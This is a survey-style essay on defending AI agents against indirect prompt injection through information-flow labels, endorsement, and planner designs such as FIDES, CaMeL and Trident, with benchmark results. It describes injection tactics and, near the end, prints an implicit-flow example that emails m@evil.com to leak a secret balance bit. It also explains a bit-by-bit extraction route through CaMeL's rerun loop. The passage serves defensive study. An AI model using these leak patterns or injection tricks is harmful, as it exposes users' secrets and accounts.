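# When an AI agent should let untrusted information shape its decisions

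## Untrusted data, trust labels and the need for exceptions

An AI agent is a program in which a language model carries out tasks by calling software tools, which are functions that read a mailbox, search the web, send a message or move money. Much of what these tools return is untrusted data, meaning data that someone the agent doesn't trust could have written or altered. For example, anyone can send an email or comment on a public code repository. If an agent lets such text shape its actions, strangers gain some control over its user's accounts. Never allowing this is safer, but it prevents the agent from doing some ordinary tasks in which the right next step depends on what a stranger wrote.

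Computer-security researchers worked on this conflict for decades before agents existed. Their main method is information-flow control, in which a system labels data, keeps the labels attached as programs use the data, and checks them before it acts. They also studied how to make exceptions to those checks without defeating them. Companies that build agents now have to decide which exceptions to allow and whether a person, a fixed rule or another model should authorize them.

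### The agent loop and indirect prompt injection

Most agents run in a loop, which *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes in a simple form. The program sends the model the conversation so far, which consists of the developer's standing instructions, the user's request, and every earlier tool call with its result. The model replies with either a final answer or a request to call a tool with specific arguments. The program, not the model, makes the call, then appends the result and queries the model again, until the model produces a final answer. The part of the agent that chooses the next action is called the planner. In the simplest agents, it is just the model reading the whole conversation.

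Suppose a user, Alex, types, "read my last three emails and, if one asks for a meeting, put it in my calendar". (The request is lightly adapted from a test case in Costa and colleagues.) The model first calls the mail tool, which adds three emails to the conversation. If the model finds a meeting request, it calls the calendar tool with a date, a time and a list of participants. Otherwise, it stops.

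In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in data the agent reads, to make the agent act for the attacker. The instructions reach the model when the tool result joins the conversation. One of the three emails might contain a sentence telling the agent to do something Alex never asked for. The sender needs no access to Alex's computer or to the model. If the model complies, the agent acts with all the permissions Alex gave it.

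*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, Nvidia, several universities and two security firms, attributes the weakness to models receiving trusted instructions and untrusted data as one stream of tokens, the small units of text they process. Nothing at that level separates the two by source. Databases once had a similar flaw, when programs pasted users' text straight into commands. Engineers largely fixed it by sending the command and the text separately, but language models have no equivalent yet.

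### How well models now resist

Developers train models to ignore injected instructions, and the models of 2026 do this much better than earlier ones. Gray Swan, a company that tests AI security, worked with the UK AI Security Institute to attack models in 19 scenarios. *Prompt Injection Robustness*, a summary of Anthropic's results for Claude Mythos Preview, reports that a single attempt succeeded 0.1% of the time, compared with about 18% for the earlier Claude Opus 4.6. Mythos Preview's rate stayed near zero even when attackers had 100 attempts. In June 2026 Anthropic reported that Claude Mythos 5 had the best score yet on a Gray Swan injection benchmark. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Mythos 5.1, published that September, describes the model as the company's most robust so far on an external test of indirect injection.

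These large gains weaken the claim in *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* that attackers keep succeeding without much extra effort. The paper's broader conjecture, that persistent attackers will always get past defences inside the model, is harder to test because a benchmark measures only the attacks its testers thought of, over a fixed number of tries. Even if the 0.1% rate held, an email service whose agents met 100,000 hostile messages could expect them to follow the instructions in about a hundred, and nobody could tell in advance which. A model that resists one kind of manipulation may also be vulnerable to related kinds. Anthropic found that Mythos 5.1, for example, was somewhat more likely than Claude Opus 5 to accept claims of authorization that it could not verify.

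Alex's request raises a difficulty that better training cannot remove. A stranger's email asking to meet on Friday at three does not appear to be an injection, and Alex told the agent to look for such emails and act on them. A model that ignored every request in its data would fail the task, but it cannot tell from the text alone whether a stranger who asks politely really wants a meeting.

### Labels and how they combine

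Information-flow control doesn't rely on the model's judgement to decide whether a tool call is allowed. Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, an article for software developers, reduces it to three steps: label each piece of data when it arrives, pass the labels on to anything the agent derives from it, and check them before each tool call. Integrity labels record how far the data's sources are trusted, and confidentiality labels record who may learn the data.

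The mathematics goes back to *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976). The paper starts from a finite set of security classes, a relation stating which classes may flow into which, and an operation that gives the class of any result computed from two inputs. Under modest assumptions these form a lattice, an ordered set in which any two elements have a least upper bound, called their join and written ⊔. Labelling a result with the join of its inputs' labels keeps the rules consistent. If a system forbade copying *a* into *c* but allowed *c* := *a* + *b*, a programmer could set *b* to zero and make the forbidden copy. A result must therefore carry a label at least as restrictive as each input's label.

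The smallest useful lattices have two levels. For confidentiality they are L (public) and H (secret), with L below H. For integrity they are T (trusted) and U (untrusted), with T below U. Trusted data is at the bottom because the order shows where data may flow. Public data may flow into a secret file, and trusted data may flow into an untrusted one, but the reverse flows are dangerous.

Denning's examples concerned secrecy. MITRE's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), by Kenneth Biba, applied the same approach to sabotage. Biba separated direct attacks, such as overwriting a protected file, from indirect ones, in which a program damages its own work by relying on data that a malicious party prepared. He compared the first to an assault with a knife and the second to poison slipped into food. Guarding against indirect attacks requires knowing where data originally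 came from and how it travelled. Indirect prompt injection is an indirect attack in Biba's sense, since the agent itself does the damage.

One of Biba's rules, the low-water mark policy, comes very close to what agent builders now use. Each program has an integrity level. When a program *s* reads an object *o*, its level becomes

il′(*s*) = min( il(*s*), il(*o*) ),

and from then on it may modify only objects at or below that new level. (Biba's scale puts high integrity at the top, so his minimum does the job of the join on the T and U scale.) In an agent, the corresponding quantity is the context label: the combined label of everything the planning model has read so far. A single label has to cover the whole context because nobody can reliably tell which parts of its input moved a language model to a given output. Costa and colleagues therefore give each output the join of the labels of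 everything the model had in front of it.

A confidentiality label is often a list of permitted readers. The join of several labels is then the intersection of their lists, so only people allowed to see every source may see the result. Here is the join for Alex's three emails. Two come from a Microsoft example in which Priya sends Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures and Marco, who isn't allowed to see them early, asks about them. Suppose that Alex's organisation trusts both colleagues and that the third email comes from a stranger.

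| Item in the conversation | Integrity | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| Alex's request | T | anyone |
| Priya's sales preview | T | Alex, Priya |
| Marco's question about sales | T | Alex, Marco |
| A stranger's request for a meeting | U | Alex, the stranger |
| Context after reading all of it | U | Alex |

The integrity part is T ⊔ T ⊔ T ⊔ U = U, so one untrusted email makes the whole context untrusted. The readers are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} ∩ {Alex, the stranger} = {Alex}. If the meeting request had come from Priya, the result would have been the same, because the stranger's email would still be in the conversation. Labels that can only become more restrictive also cause problems in long sessions.

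### The trusted-action policy

The labels matter once a rule refers to them. The basic one concerns consequential actions, tool calls with effects that matter, such as a payment, a message or a deletion. It permits such a call only if the planner chose it in a trusted context. Costa and colleagues write the condition for a call to tool *f* with *n* arguments as

ℓ_f ⊔ ℓ₁ ⊔ … ⊔ ℓₙ = T,

where ℓ_f is the integrity label on the choice of the tool and the others are the labels on its arguments. A looser variant checks only the choice of tool and the most sensitive arguments, such as the recipient of a message. A companion rule protects secrets: data may leave through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is among the data's permitted readers. On its own the companion rule does not prevent injection. It limits what a hijacked agent can leak.

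Ordinary code performs the check outside the model, so if the labels are right, no wording in an email can change the outcome. Costa and colleagues tested this on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and chat tasks with planted injections. They found that 152 attacks succeeded against a basic agent built on GPT-4o, and none succeeded with the policies switched on. GPT-4o is an old model, and fewer of the attacks would succeed against today's models, but the zero result comes from the policy and doesn't depend on the model's resistance.

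With no attack under way, the policies reduced the share of banking tasks that the same basic agent completed from 98.8% to 37.5%. Many of those tasks require the agent to read a file and then do what the file asks, such as scheduling a payment, which the rule forbids. Alex's request fails for the same reason. After the emails arrive, the context label is U, so the system refuses the calendar call. The agent can still tell Alex that someone wants to meet on Friday, because Costa and colleagues do not count replies to the user as consequential, but Alex has to make the calendar entry by hand.

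Better engineering recovers part of the loss. If a planner never sees untrusted data, its context stays trusted and it can still finish many tasks, but not Alex's.

### Noninterference, and why the calendar task breaks it

The ideal behind these rules is noninterference, the property that a given class of inputs makes no difference to given outputs. For secrecy, the inputs are the secrets and the outputs are whatever outsiders can observe. For integrity, the inputs are the untrusted data and the outputs are the agent's consequential actions. Write *d* for everything the agent could read, *A*(*d*) for the consequential actions it then takes, and *d*₁ =_T *d*₂ when two such collections agree on every trusted item. The agent satisfies noninterference if, for all *d*₁ and *d*₂,

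*d*₁ =_T *d*₂ ⇒ *A*(*d*₁) = *A*(*d*₂).

Suppose two versions of Alex's mailbox are identical except that the stranger's email asks for a meeting in the first and advertises shoes in the second. The trusted data is the same in both, so noninterference requires the agent to do the same thing to the calendar. Alex's request requires a new entry in the first case and none in the second, so no agent can satisfy both the request and noninterference, however capable its model.

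The influence is there even when the agent does nothing. Denning called this an implicit flow and gave the example of a program line that copies *c* into *b* only if *a* equals zero. Information passes from *a* to *b* whether or not the line copies anything, because anyone who sees *b* unchanged may learn that *a* was not zero. The "if" in Alex's request creates the same kind of flow. Practical systems usually enforce something weaker than noninterference. Costa and colleagues prove that their checks stop secret data from flowing directly into places an attacker can see, but an observer could still learn a little from which tools the agent calls and in what order. They judged full noninterference too restrictive because it would in effect forbid an agent to write anywhere public once it had read anything secret.

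### Declassification and endorsement

Security theory calls the two deliberate ways of breaking the rule declassification and endorsement. Declassification releases some secret data to people who could not otherwise see it. For example, once the agent has read Priya's preview, only Alex may read a reply it then writes to Marco, so the system should hold the reply back. If Alex decides to let Marco have the figures, sending them is a declassification. Endorsement, the counterpart for integrity, treats some untrusted data as trusted. Both move data down the lattice, from H to L or from U to T, which the ordinary rules forbid.

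The calendar task needs an endorsement. At minimum, the system must endorse the yes-or-no answer to whether any of the emails contains a meeting request. If the policy also covers the arguments of the call, the system must endorse the date, time and participants too, which lets the stranger influence what the entry contains as well as whether it exists. Endorsing the full text of the email would let the planner act on anything in it, and Alex would be back to relying on the model's training. If the calendar sends out invitations, inviting anyone else would also require a declassification, because only Alex is allowed to read the context.

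An endorsement is a decision that a certain amount of influence from untrusted data is acceptable for a certain purpose. It does not make the data true, so a stranger who doesn't intend to turn up can still put a meeting in Alex's calendar. Each endorsement needs an authorizer, which is the person, rule or model whose decision makes the exception valid.

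## Which tasks can be done without acting on untrusted data

Alex's calendar request needs an endorsement because the right action depends on what a stranger wrote. Many other requests don't need one. For example, an agent can forward three emails without any model reading them. The planner's context then stays trusted, so the planner can choose the next action without an exception.

### Data-independent tasks

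Costa and colleagues give a formal test for such tasks. They describe a task *t* by the user's request, the available tools and a set *D* of states the data might be in when the agent starts. For each state *d*, ⟦*t*⟧(*d*) is the set of action sequences that would complete the task. An action here is a tool call or the final answer to the user, and the planner's own queries to its language model do not count. The task is data-independent if

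⋂_{*d* ∈ *D*} ⟦*t*⟧(*d*) ≠ ∅.

In words, one sequence of tool calls and one final answer must work for every possible state of the data. If no such sequence exists, the task is data-dependent. Here are three requests, adapted from the paper:

- **"Send my last three emails to Priya in a chat message."** The agent reads three emails and sends the result to Priya. This works whatever the emails contain, so the task is data-independent.
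- **"Summarize my last three emails and send Priya the summary."** The sequence is now read, summarize, send. It also works for every mailbox.
- **"Read my last three emails and, if one asks for a meeting, put it in my calendar."** No single sequence suits both a mailbox with a meeting request and one without, so the task is data-dependent.

An agent can forward or summarize email without acting on untrusted data only if an argument in a tool call can be a reference, such as "whatever the mail tool returned". If every argument had to be literal text, the agent would have to write a different message for each mailbox, and very few tasks would qualify.

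A data-dependent task does not always need an exception, because *D* also covers trusted data. If the plan depends only on data that no attacker can write, the planner can read that data and its context stays trusted. Costa and colleagues saw this in a banking task that asks the agent to change a password if it finds a suspicious transaction. They had labelled amounts and dates as trusted and descriptions as untrusted. The planner saw a large amount, judged it suspicious and changed the password without reading any descriptions. The policy allowed this, although an amount alone is weak evidence of fraud.

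### Hiding text from the planner

The basic design for keeping untrusted text away from the planner comes from a blog post, *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023). Willison imagined an assistant called Marvin that could update a to-do list from a colleague's latest email. The obstacle was that a stranger could send an email telling Marvin to delete the user's whole mailbox.

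Willison's pattern divides the work between two models. One plans and calls tools but does not read untrusted text. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted text but cannot call tools, and ordinary code carries results between the two. An attacker who takes over the quarantined model can make it return bad text but cannot make it send or delete anything.

The planner still has to refer to text it cannot see, and variables make this possible. In the variable-passing planner that Costa and colleagues describe, the forwarding task runs as follows:

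1. The planner asks the mail tool for three emails.
2. The program stores the emails in memory under a new name, such as `#read_emails_0`, and adds only that name to the conversation.
3. The planner calls the chat tool with Priya as the recipient and `#read_emails_0` as the message.
4. The program replaces the name with the stored emails and makes the call.

The planner's context never contains the emails, so it keeps the label T (trusted). The message is still labeled U (untrusted), so the strict form of the trusted-action policy would block the call, but the looser form would allow it.

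Summarizing takes one more step. After the program stores the emails, the planner calls the quarantined model to summarize `#read_emails_0`. The program stores the summary under another name, and the planner sends it to Priya without reading it.

FIDES, the full system that Costa and colleagues built, compares the label of each part of a tool result with the context label and hides a part in a variable only if showing it to the planner would make the context label more restrictive. The planner might see the date of an email, for example, but not its subject or body.

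Untrusted data can still influence a planner that cannot read it. In one run of the variable-passing planner, the user asked the agent to find the chat channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. The program hid the channel names and the messages, but the planner could still see how many messages each channel returned. It picked an empty channel and passed the hidden name to the tool. Anyone able to post in that channel could have changed the outcome by raising its message count, which the labels did not cover.

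The planner cannot complete Alex's calendar request using variables alone, because it holds only the name `#read_emails_0` and cannot determine whether to call the calendar tool. A yes-or-no answer from the quarantined model would be enough if the system endorsed it.

### Plans written as code

CaMeL, a system Google DeepMind researchers published in 2025, replaces the list of tool calls with a program. Willison explains that CaMeL turns a command such as "Send Bob the document he requested in our last meeting" into steps in a Python-like language, then checks the data going into and out of each step. According to *Trident* (2026), which presents a later defence of the same name, CaMeL's planning model writes the program before it reads any data. A quarantined model extracts values from untrusted data as the program runs, and a data-flow policy can block individual tool calls.

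A program can contain branches, which a fixed list of calls cannot. For Alex's request, it might look like this:

```
emails = read_emails(3)
found = quarantined_model("Find a meeting request", emails)
if found.exists:
    create_event(found.date, found.time, found.participants)
```

The planner can write these lines without seeing the mailbox. When the program runs, it creates an event for one mailbox and does nothing for another. CaMeL's code can branch on values in the data, but the planner cannot write a new plan after the program has read them. If the stranger's email says that guests must first register on a website, the program has no step for that unless the planner anticipated it.

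Branching does not remove the need for an endorsement either, since the stranger still decides whether `create_event` runs. It does limit the stranger to outcomes already in the program. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) uses almost the same calendar request as an example of what these defences handle badly. The paper says that CaMeL asks the user to endorse the action, and that nobody has a principled account of which such tasks an agent can do securely.

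CaMeL seems to lose little performance on the AgentDojo benchmark by fixing its program in advance. Narisetty and colleagues cite results in which it completed 77% of tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an undefended agent, while using almost three times as many tokens. How far this result applies to other work depends on how many AgentDojo tasks require the agent to adapt to what it reads.

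### How many AgentDojo tasks depend on the data

Costa and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's 97 user tasks by hand, separating the data-independent tasks that need a quarantined model from those that do not. The counts below follow from their percentages and the number of tasks in each suite.

| Suite | Tasks | Independent, no quarantined model needed | Independent, quarantined model needed | Data-dependent |
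|---|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 40 | 19 (47.5%) | 19 (47.5%) | 2 (5.0%) |
| Travel | 20 | 0 | 18 (90.0%) | 2 (10.0%) |
| Banking | 16 | 3 (18.7%) | 6 (37.5%) | 7 (43.8%) |
| Slack | 21 | 4 (19.0%) | 8 (38.1%) | 9 (42.9%) |
| All | 97 | 26 (26.8%) | 51 (52.6%) | 20 (20.6%) |

For about four-fifths of the tasks, the agent could settle on a plan before reading anything. The rest are data-dependent, and they make up only 5% of the workspace tasks but 43.8% of the banking tasks.

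*AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) gives a much lower count, finding that only 6 of the 97 tasks need dynamic planning. The two counts probably measure different things. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks for a hotel reservation if the hotel's rating is above 4. The task is data-dependent because the rating determines whether the agent should make a reservation. Yet a planner can write "if the rating is above 4, reserve" before it sees the rating, and it never has to revise that plan. The count of 20 includes conditional tasks like this one, while the count of 6 appears to cover only tasks in which the agent must work out new steps along the way. If so, about 14 tasks need data, trusted or untrusted, to choose between known outcomes but do not need a new plan.

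By either count, AgentDojo contains little open-ended work, and some of its scores overstate what a planner can do without reading untrusted data. All of the travel tasks require some model to read such data, yet the variable-passing planner completed 43% of them with GPT-4o and no quarantined model. Costa and colleagues found that it sometimes guessed, such as when it recommended the right hotel without seeing any reviews. In other tasks, the correct behaviour was to do nothing. OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, completed only 2% of the travel tasks under the same restrictions, much closer to the result expected from the table.

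### AgentDyn and tasks that need a new plan

Li and colleagues built the AgentDyn benchmark to fill this gap. It has 60 user tasks, split equally among shopping, managing GitHub code repositories and daily life. Pairing them with 28 attacker goals gives 560 test cases. The tasks take 7.1 steps on average, compared with about 3.5 in AgentDojo, and use more than twice as many applications.

Every AgentDyn task requires the agent to change its plan while working and includes at least one helpful instruction in the data the agent has to read. For example, a bank tool might reject a payment over $500 until the agent fetches a one-time password from the user's inbox, or a GitHub tool might return an instruction to download recent changes before uploading new ones. An agent that ignores all instructions in tool results cannot finish these tasks. AgentDyn places malicious instructions only where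 an outsider could plausibly put them, such as in a web page's advertising banner.

Li and colleagues tested CaMeL and several other kinds of defence. DRIFT writes an initial plan with security constraints and uses a second check to decide whether the agent may depart from it. Progent has a language model write rules about which tools the agent may use and update them as results arrive. ProtectAI, PIGuard and PromptGuard 2 are filters, small models trained to recognize injected instructions. These are the results with GPT-4o as the agent's model:

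| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
| ProtectAI | 0% | 0.6% | 0.9% |
| PIGuard | 10.0% | 1.5% | 1.7% |
| PromptGuard 2 | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |

CaMeL completed no tasks with any of the 12 models tested. Li and colleagues attribute this to its static program, which cannot add steps that the agent discovers later. A planner could in theory write a branch for every password check and upload conflict in advance, but none of the models wrote enough of these branches.

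The other defences failed for different reasons. DRIFT allowed some changes to its initial plan but still relied heavily on it. Progent struggled to assign the right permissions when an agent had more than 30 tools, and its mistakes accumulated until it blocked almost everything useful. ProtectAI and PIGuard could not tell helpful instructions from malicious ones. PromptGuard 2 interfered little in the absence of an attack, but when it detected an injection, it discarded the entire tool result, including information the agent needed.

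The first of three limits on these figures is the age of the models. GPT-4o dates from 2024, and Li and colleagues chose it and similar models for their main comparison partly because newer ones had probably learned to resist the standard attack. With no defence, Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 71.7% of the tasks, and 0.9% of the attacks succeeded. Adding DRIFT lowered the attack success rate by only 0.7 percentage points, to 0.2%, but lowered task completion by 43.4 points, to 28.3%.

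That comparison depends on the attacks, which Li and colleagues call relatively weak against frontier models. When they tailored attacks to each scenario, the success rate against undefended Sonnet 4.5 rose to 3.0%. A determined attacker might succeed more often, so the benchmark is stronger evidence about lost usefulness than about safety.

The third limit is that no user was available to approve the agents' steps. Agents often stopped to ask for confirmation, so Li and colleagues instructed them to complete every task without it. CaMeL's 0% therefore does not show how it would perform if a user could approve the steps it refused.

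AgentDyn also does not distinguish needing a new plan from needing to act on untrusted data. A request for a one-time password from the user's own bank could reasonably be labeled trusted. A planner that may read trusted tool results, like the one in FIDES, could then respond to it without any exception, whereas CaMeL would fail because its program is already fixed. Li and colleagues did not test FIDES, which might have done better on such steps.

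### ReplanInject and Trident

*Trident* introduces ReplanInject, a benchmark that comes closer to measuring the need for exceptions. All 45 tasks require the agent to read untrusted content, and the attacker's text sits inside that same content. The researchers graded the tasks by how much each request leaves for the content to decide:

- In 2 tasks, the request names every action.
- In 22 tasks, the request names the action, and the content settles a condition or a choice, such as whether a venue is confirmed.
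- In 18 tasks, the content determines which actions to take and how many.
- In 3 tasks, the user names a source and leaves everything else to it, for example by asking the agent to "do what this email says".

In one request of the third kind, the user's manager, Jane, has forwarded an email from a caterer. The user asks the agent to do what the email asks, pay from the team account and tell Jane when it is done. The request specifies the email's sender, its subject and the account to use, but the tasks are in the email. An injected line saying that the caterer's bank details have changed looks like ordinary business correspondence. The paper concludes that for these "do what this email says" tasks, no policy can always tell the user's intention from the attacker's.

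The Trident system lets its planner revise the plan without showing it the untrusted text. It uses three language models. The planner chooses actions but sees only references to the untrusted text. A data model reads the text and has no tools. A policy model writes the rules for the task from the user's request and the organization's standing policy, before any model reads the untrusted text. Ordinary code checks each model's output before it takes effect.

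The planner gets information about the text by sending the data model questions with a finite list of possible answers, and it can make a new plan after each answer. In one recorded run, the user wanted the cheapest equipment offer that could arrive by a deadline. The planner checked whether each of two offers could meet the date, and the answer was yes for only one. It then looked up the supplier's account in past transactions and paid the price in the offer without receiving the figure. The attacker had added a different account number to that offer, but the number never reached the planner.

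Trident measures these answers in bits and counts them against two limits that an administrator sets, β for information the planner receives from the data and σ for signals such as whether a call failed. The researchers proved that an attacker can then choose among at most 2^(β+σ) visible courses of action, with the trusted inputs, the user's decisions and the models' randomness held fixed. They also checked the proof in Lean, a language for computer-verified mathematics. The equipment run used 10.8 bits of one limit and 4 of the other. Limits of exactly that size would allow about 28,500 courses of action, some of which may still be harmful, because the theorem restricts only their number.

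The researchers compared Trident with other defences on 360 attacked runs, repeated three times. The table gives the results for two of their four models. The last two columns show how often attacks succeeded when every request to the user was approved automatically.

| Defence | Tasks completed under attack, GPT-4.1 | Tasks completed under attack, Sonnet 4.5 | Successful attacks, GPT-4.1 | Successful attacks, Sonnet 4.5 |
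|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 20.2% | 58.9% | 68.1% | 12.9% |
| CaMeL | 9.8% | 8.8% | 0% | 0% |
| FIDES, no approvals | 5.1% | 3.3% | 0.1% | 0% |
| FIDES, with approvals | 36.6% | 75.2% | 6.5% | 6.0% |
| Progent | 35.4% | 55.7% | 33.1% | 7.0% |
| Trident | 54.2% | 64.4% | 4.1% | 3.4% |

Missing steps caused only some of CaMeL's failures here. With GPT-4.1, it completed 116 of 1,215 runs, a total that includes runs without an attack. In 574 others, nearly half of all runs, its policy blocked a call that contained nothing from the attacker because the call depended on untrusted data, and CaMeL had no exception for legitimate actions. In another 377, the quarantined model failed to extract what the program needed.

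Trident completed every run in which the request named all the actions. With Sonnet 4.5, it completed 89.5% of attacked runs on the 27 tasks in which the content doesn't choose the actions. On the other 18, it completed only 22.0% to 41.4%, depending on the model. FIDES with approvals did better overall with Sonnet 4.5 because it did better on those 18 tasks. But its planner read free text derived from untrusted data in 90% of its runs, and after that the user's review was the only check.

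Only one of the 48 failed Trident runs that the researchers examined needed text the system had kept hidden. In 27, the planner chose the wrong record, value or tool, and in 18 the data model answered wrongly or the planner stopped too early. Stronger models could therefore narrow the gap without any change to the security design.

No attack in ReplanInject succeeded against Trident if the user rejected every request that showed the attacker's action. That assumes a perfectly attentive user, while the table shows the worst case. The same researchers designed ReplanInject and Trident, and they avoided the latest models so that attacks would succeed often enough to compare defences. Trident also cost $0.10 to $0.24 per run, several times as much as an undefended agent. On the 20 data-dependent tasks in AgentDojo, which other people wrote, Trident completed 52.7% to 64.4% of attacked runs, compared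 with 13.7% to 21.9% for CaMeL and FIDES without approvals.

### Harm that leaves the plan unchanged

A secure plan determines which tools the agent uses and in what order, but not what the quarantined model writes. Costa and colleagues point out that one of the emails could contain an instruction to produce an empty summary. The agent would still read, summarize and send as planned, but Priya would receive nothing useful. A subtler attack could make the model leave out one email or reverse its meaning.

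One AgentDojo attack tries to make the agent tell the user that a place is gorgeous and worth a visit. Costa and colleagues did not count such cases as successful injections, since no tool call changed and no secret leaked. Narisetty and colleagues note that CaMeL's designers also put this kind of harm outside their aims, and *Trident* does not claim to prevent misleading summaries. This may be acceptable for a hotel tip, but it is harder to accept when someone relies on a summary of a contract or a medical record. Narisetty and colleagues expect the problem to grow as people act on more text written by agents. The summary keeps its untrusted label, so an application could display a warning or withhold the text.

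Corrupted arguments can do more direct damage. Suppose a user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file. The agent always reads the file, extracts the account and amount, and sends the money, so the task is data-independent and the planner doesn't need to see the bill. But someone who can edit the file can insert another account number, and the agent will then pay the wrong person even though it follows the correct plan. In their test, Costa and colleagues used a policy for payments that checked the label on the choice of tool but ignored the labels on the arguments. None of the planted injections succeeded in this way, but the policy would not have blocked such a payment.

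Requiring every argument to be trusted would close the gap, but it would also prevent the agent from paying any bill whose details arrive by email, or forwarding a stranger's message to Priya. A task that needs no exception for the choice of action may still need one for an argument.

Trident applies a separate rule to each argument of a payment. In the caterer example, the amount may come from the untrusted invoice if it is below $5,000. The account number must come from the company's vendor records, which the caterer cannot edit. An injected account number therefore fails the check, but a false invoice could still lead the agent to overpay the real caterer by thousands of dollars.

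## How labels spread until the agent can do little

Variables and programs written in advance can keep untrusted text out of the planner's context. But the simple agent loop adds every tool result to the conversation, so one email from a stranger can stop the agent from doing unrelated work.

### A six-step run

Suppose Alex types, "Check when Friday's workshop starts, tell Priya I'll be there, see what new email I have, pay the venue deposit to the account I saved, delete my old draft agenda, and tell me what you did." Only colleagues can edit the team calendar, so its entries count as trusted. The table shows the integrity label under the basic trusted-action policy.

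| Step | What the agent tries to do | Context before | Does the policy allow it? | Context after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read the team calendar | T | Yes | T |
| 2 | Message Priya | T | Yes | T |
| 3 | Read new emails, including one from a stranger | T | Yes | U |
| 4 | Pay the deposit | U | No | U |
| 5 | Delete the draft | U | No | U |
| 6 | Report to Alex | U | Yes | U |

After step 3, the policy blocks every consequential action for the rest of the conversation, even if the stranger only advertised shoes. Alex supplied everything the payment and the deletion require, but the check uses a single label for the whole context. That label is a join, so adding trusted data cannot return it to T. The policy would have allowed all six steps if the agent had paid the deposit and deleted the draft before it opened the mail.

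The label can also spread beyond the conversation. Under Costa and colleagues' rules, data that a tool writes gets the join of the labels on the call, its arguments and everything the tool read. If the policy lets the agent save a note after step 3, the note is untrusted, and any later conversation in which the agent reads it becomes untrusted too.

Researchers call the tendency of labels to grow more and more restrictive until the system allows little "label creep". *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) credits the idea to a 2003 survey by Andrei Sabelfeld and Andrew Myers. Biba's 1977 low-water mark policy already had this tendency, because a program's integrity level could only fall.

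Language models make label creep worse. In ordinary code, the line `c = a + b` depends on `a` and `b`, so an untrusted `d` elsewhere in the program leaves `c` trusted. In a language model, any token in the context may influence any token of the output, so the output has to carry the label of the whole context.

### What creep costs

Costa and colleagues measured the cost on AgentDojo by running the simple planner and FIDES, which hides untrusted data in variables, with and without policy checks. These are the shares of tasks completed with no attack under way:

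| Planner and model | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Simple, GPT-4o, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Simple, GPT-4o, checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, GPT-4o, no checks | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, GPT-4o, checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |
| Simple, o1, checks | 48.0% | 75.0% | 37.5% | 17.1% |
| FIDES, o1, checks | 64.5% | 68.0% | 56.2% | 54.3% |

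With GPT-4o, the checks stopped the simple planner from completing about half of its workspace tasks and nearly four-fifths of its Slack tasks. Travel tasks saw no such loss because the tested policies were looser than the basic rule for some tools. They let an agent send an email or create a calendar event from an untrusted context if every recipient was allowed to read the contents and the message contained no untrusted link. Payments, deletions and password changes always required a trusted context.

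The checks lowered FIDES's score much less, by between 4.5 percentage points in workspace and 16.2 in Slack. But its score without them was also lower, because GPT-4o often mixed up variable names or failed to use the quarantined model. With the checks on, FIDES averaged about 8 points more than the simple planner across the four suites when both used GPT-4o, and about 16 points more when both used o1.

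Most of that second gain came from FIDES. Moving from GPT-4o to o1 raised the simple planner's average by only 2.5 points, because a more capable model's actions are still refused when the context is untrusted. FIDES gained almost 11 points because o1 handled variables better. With o1, FIDES scored 56.2% on banking, which equals the share of banking tasks that are data-independent. Its Slack score was close to the 57.1% of Slack tasks that are data-independent. In those two suites, a better model could add little without an exception for untrusted data. There was still room to improve in workspace and travel, where at least 90% of tasks are data-independent.

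Two details of the tests affect how far the losses carry over to real deployments. Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if any AgentDojo attack targeted it, so every email body was untrusted, even in mail from a colleague. An organisation that can authenticate its own senders would lose fewer tasks. The planner also caused some of the label spread. In one Slack task, GPT-4o listed all the channels although the user had named the one to use, and that call lowered the integrity of the context.

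### Influence without copying

The measured losses would have been larger if FIDES had tracked every kind of influence. Its labels follow data that the agent copies or feeds to a model, but they do not fully cover implicit flows, such as the one from the "if" in Alex's calendar request.

The computer scientist J. S. Fenton first described an example that shows how hard implicit flows are to catch. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) adapts it to an agent that manages a customer's account, and the program below follows that version. The balance is secret, the other variables start out public, and the attacker wants to know whether the balance exceeds a threshold.

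```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

Suppose a monitor watches the program run and labels a variable secret whenever the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret. There are two cases:

- **The balance is high.** The program sets `tmp` to false, and the monitor labels it secret. The next branch does not run, so nothing changes `rich`, which stays true and public. The program sends the email.
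- **The balance is low.** The program skips the first branch, so `tmp` stays true and public. The next branch runs on a public condition and sets `rich` to false, which also stays public. The program sends nothing.

Either way, `rich` reveals the secret while carrying a public label. The monitor misses the leak because it comes from a line that did not run. Garby and colleagues found this flaw in CaMeL's interpreter, though CaMeL catches the simpler program that sends the email directly from a branch on the balance.

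A standard remedy, called no-high-upgrade, forbids a program from changing public data inside a branch that depends on a secret. With a high balance, the program stops at `tmp = False` and sends nothing. The rule also stops harmless programs, and an observer can infer from the stop that the balance was high. This leaks only one bit, but CaMeL reruns failed programs from a loop outside the monitored code. Garby and colleagues point out that an attacker could use this loop to extract a whole secret one bit at a time.

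### Explicit secrecy and noninterference

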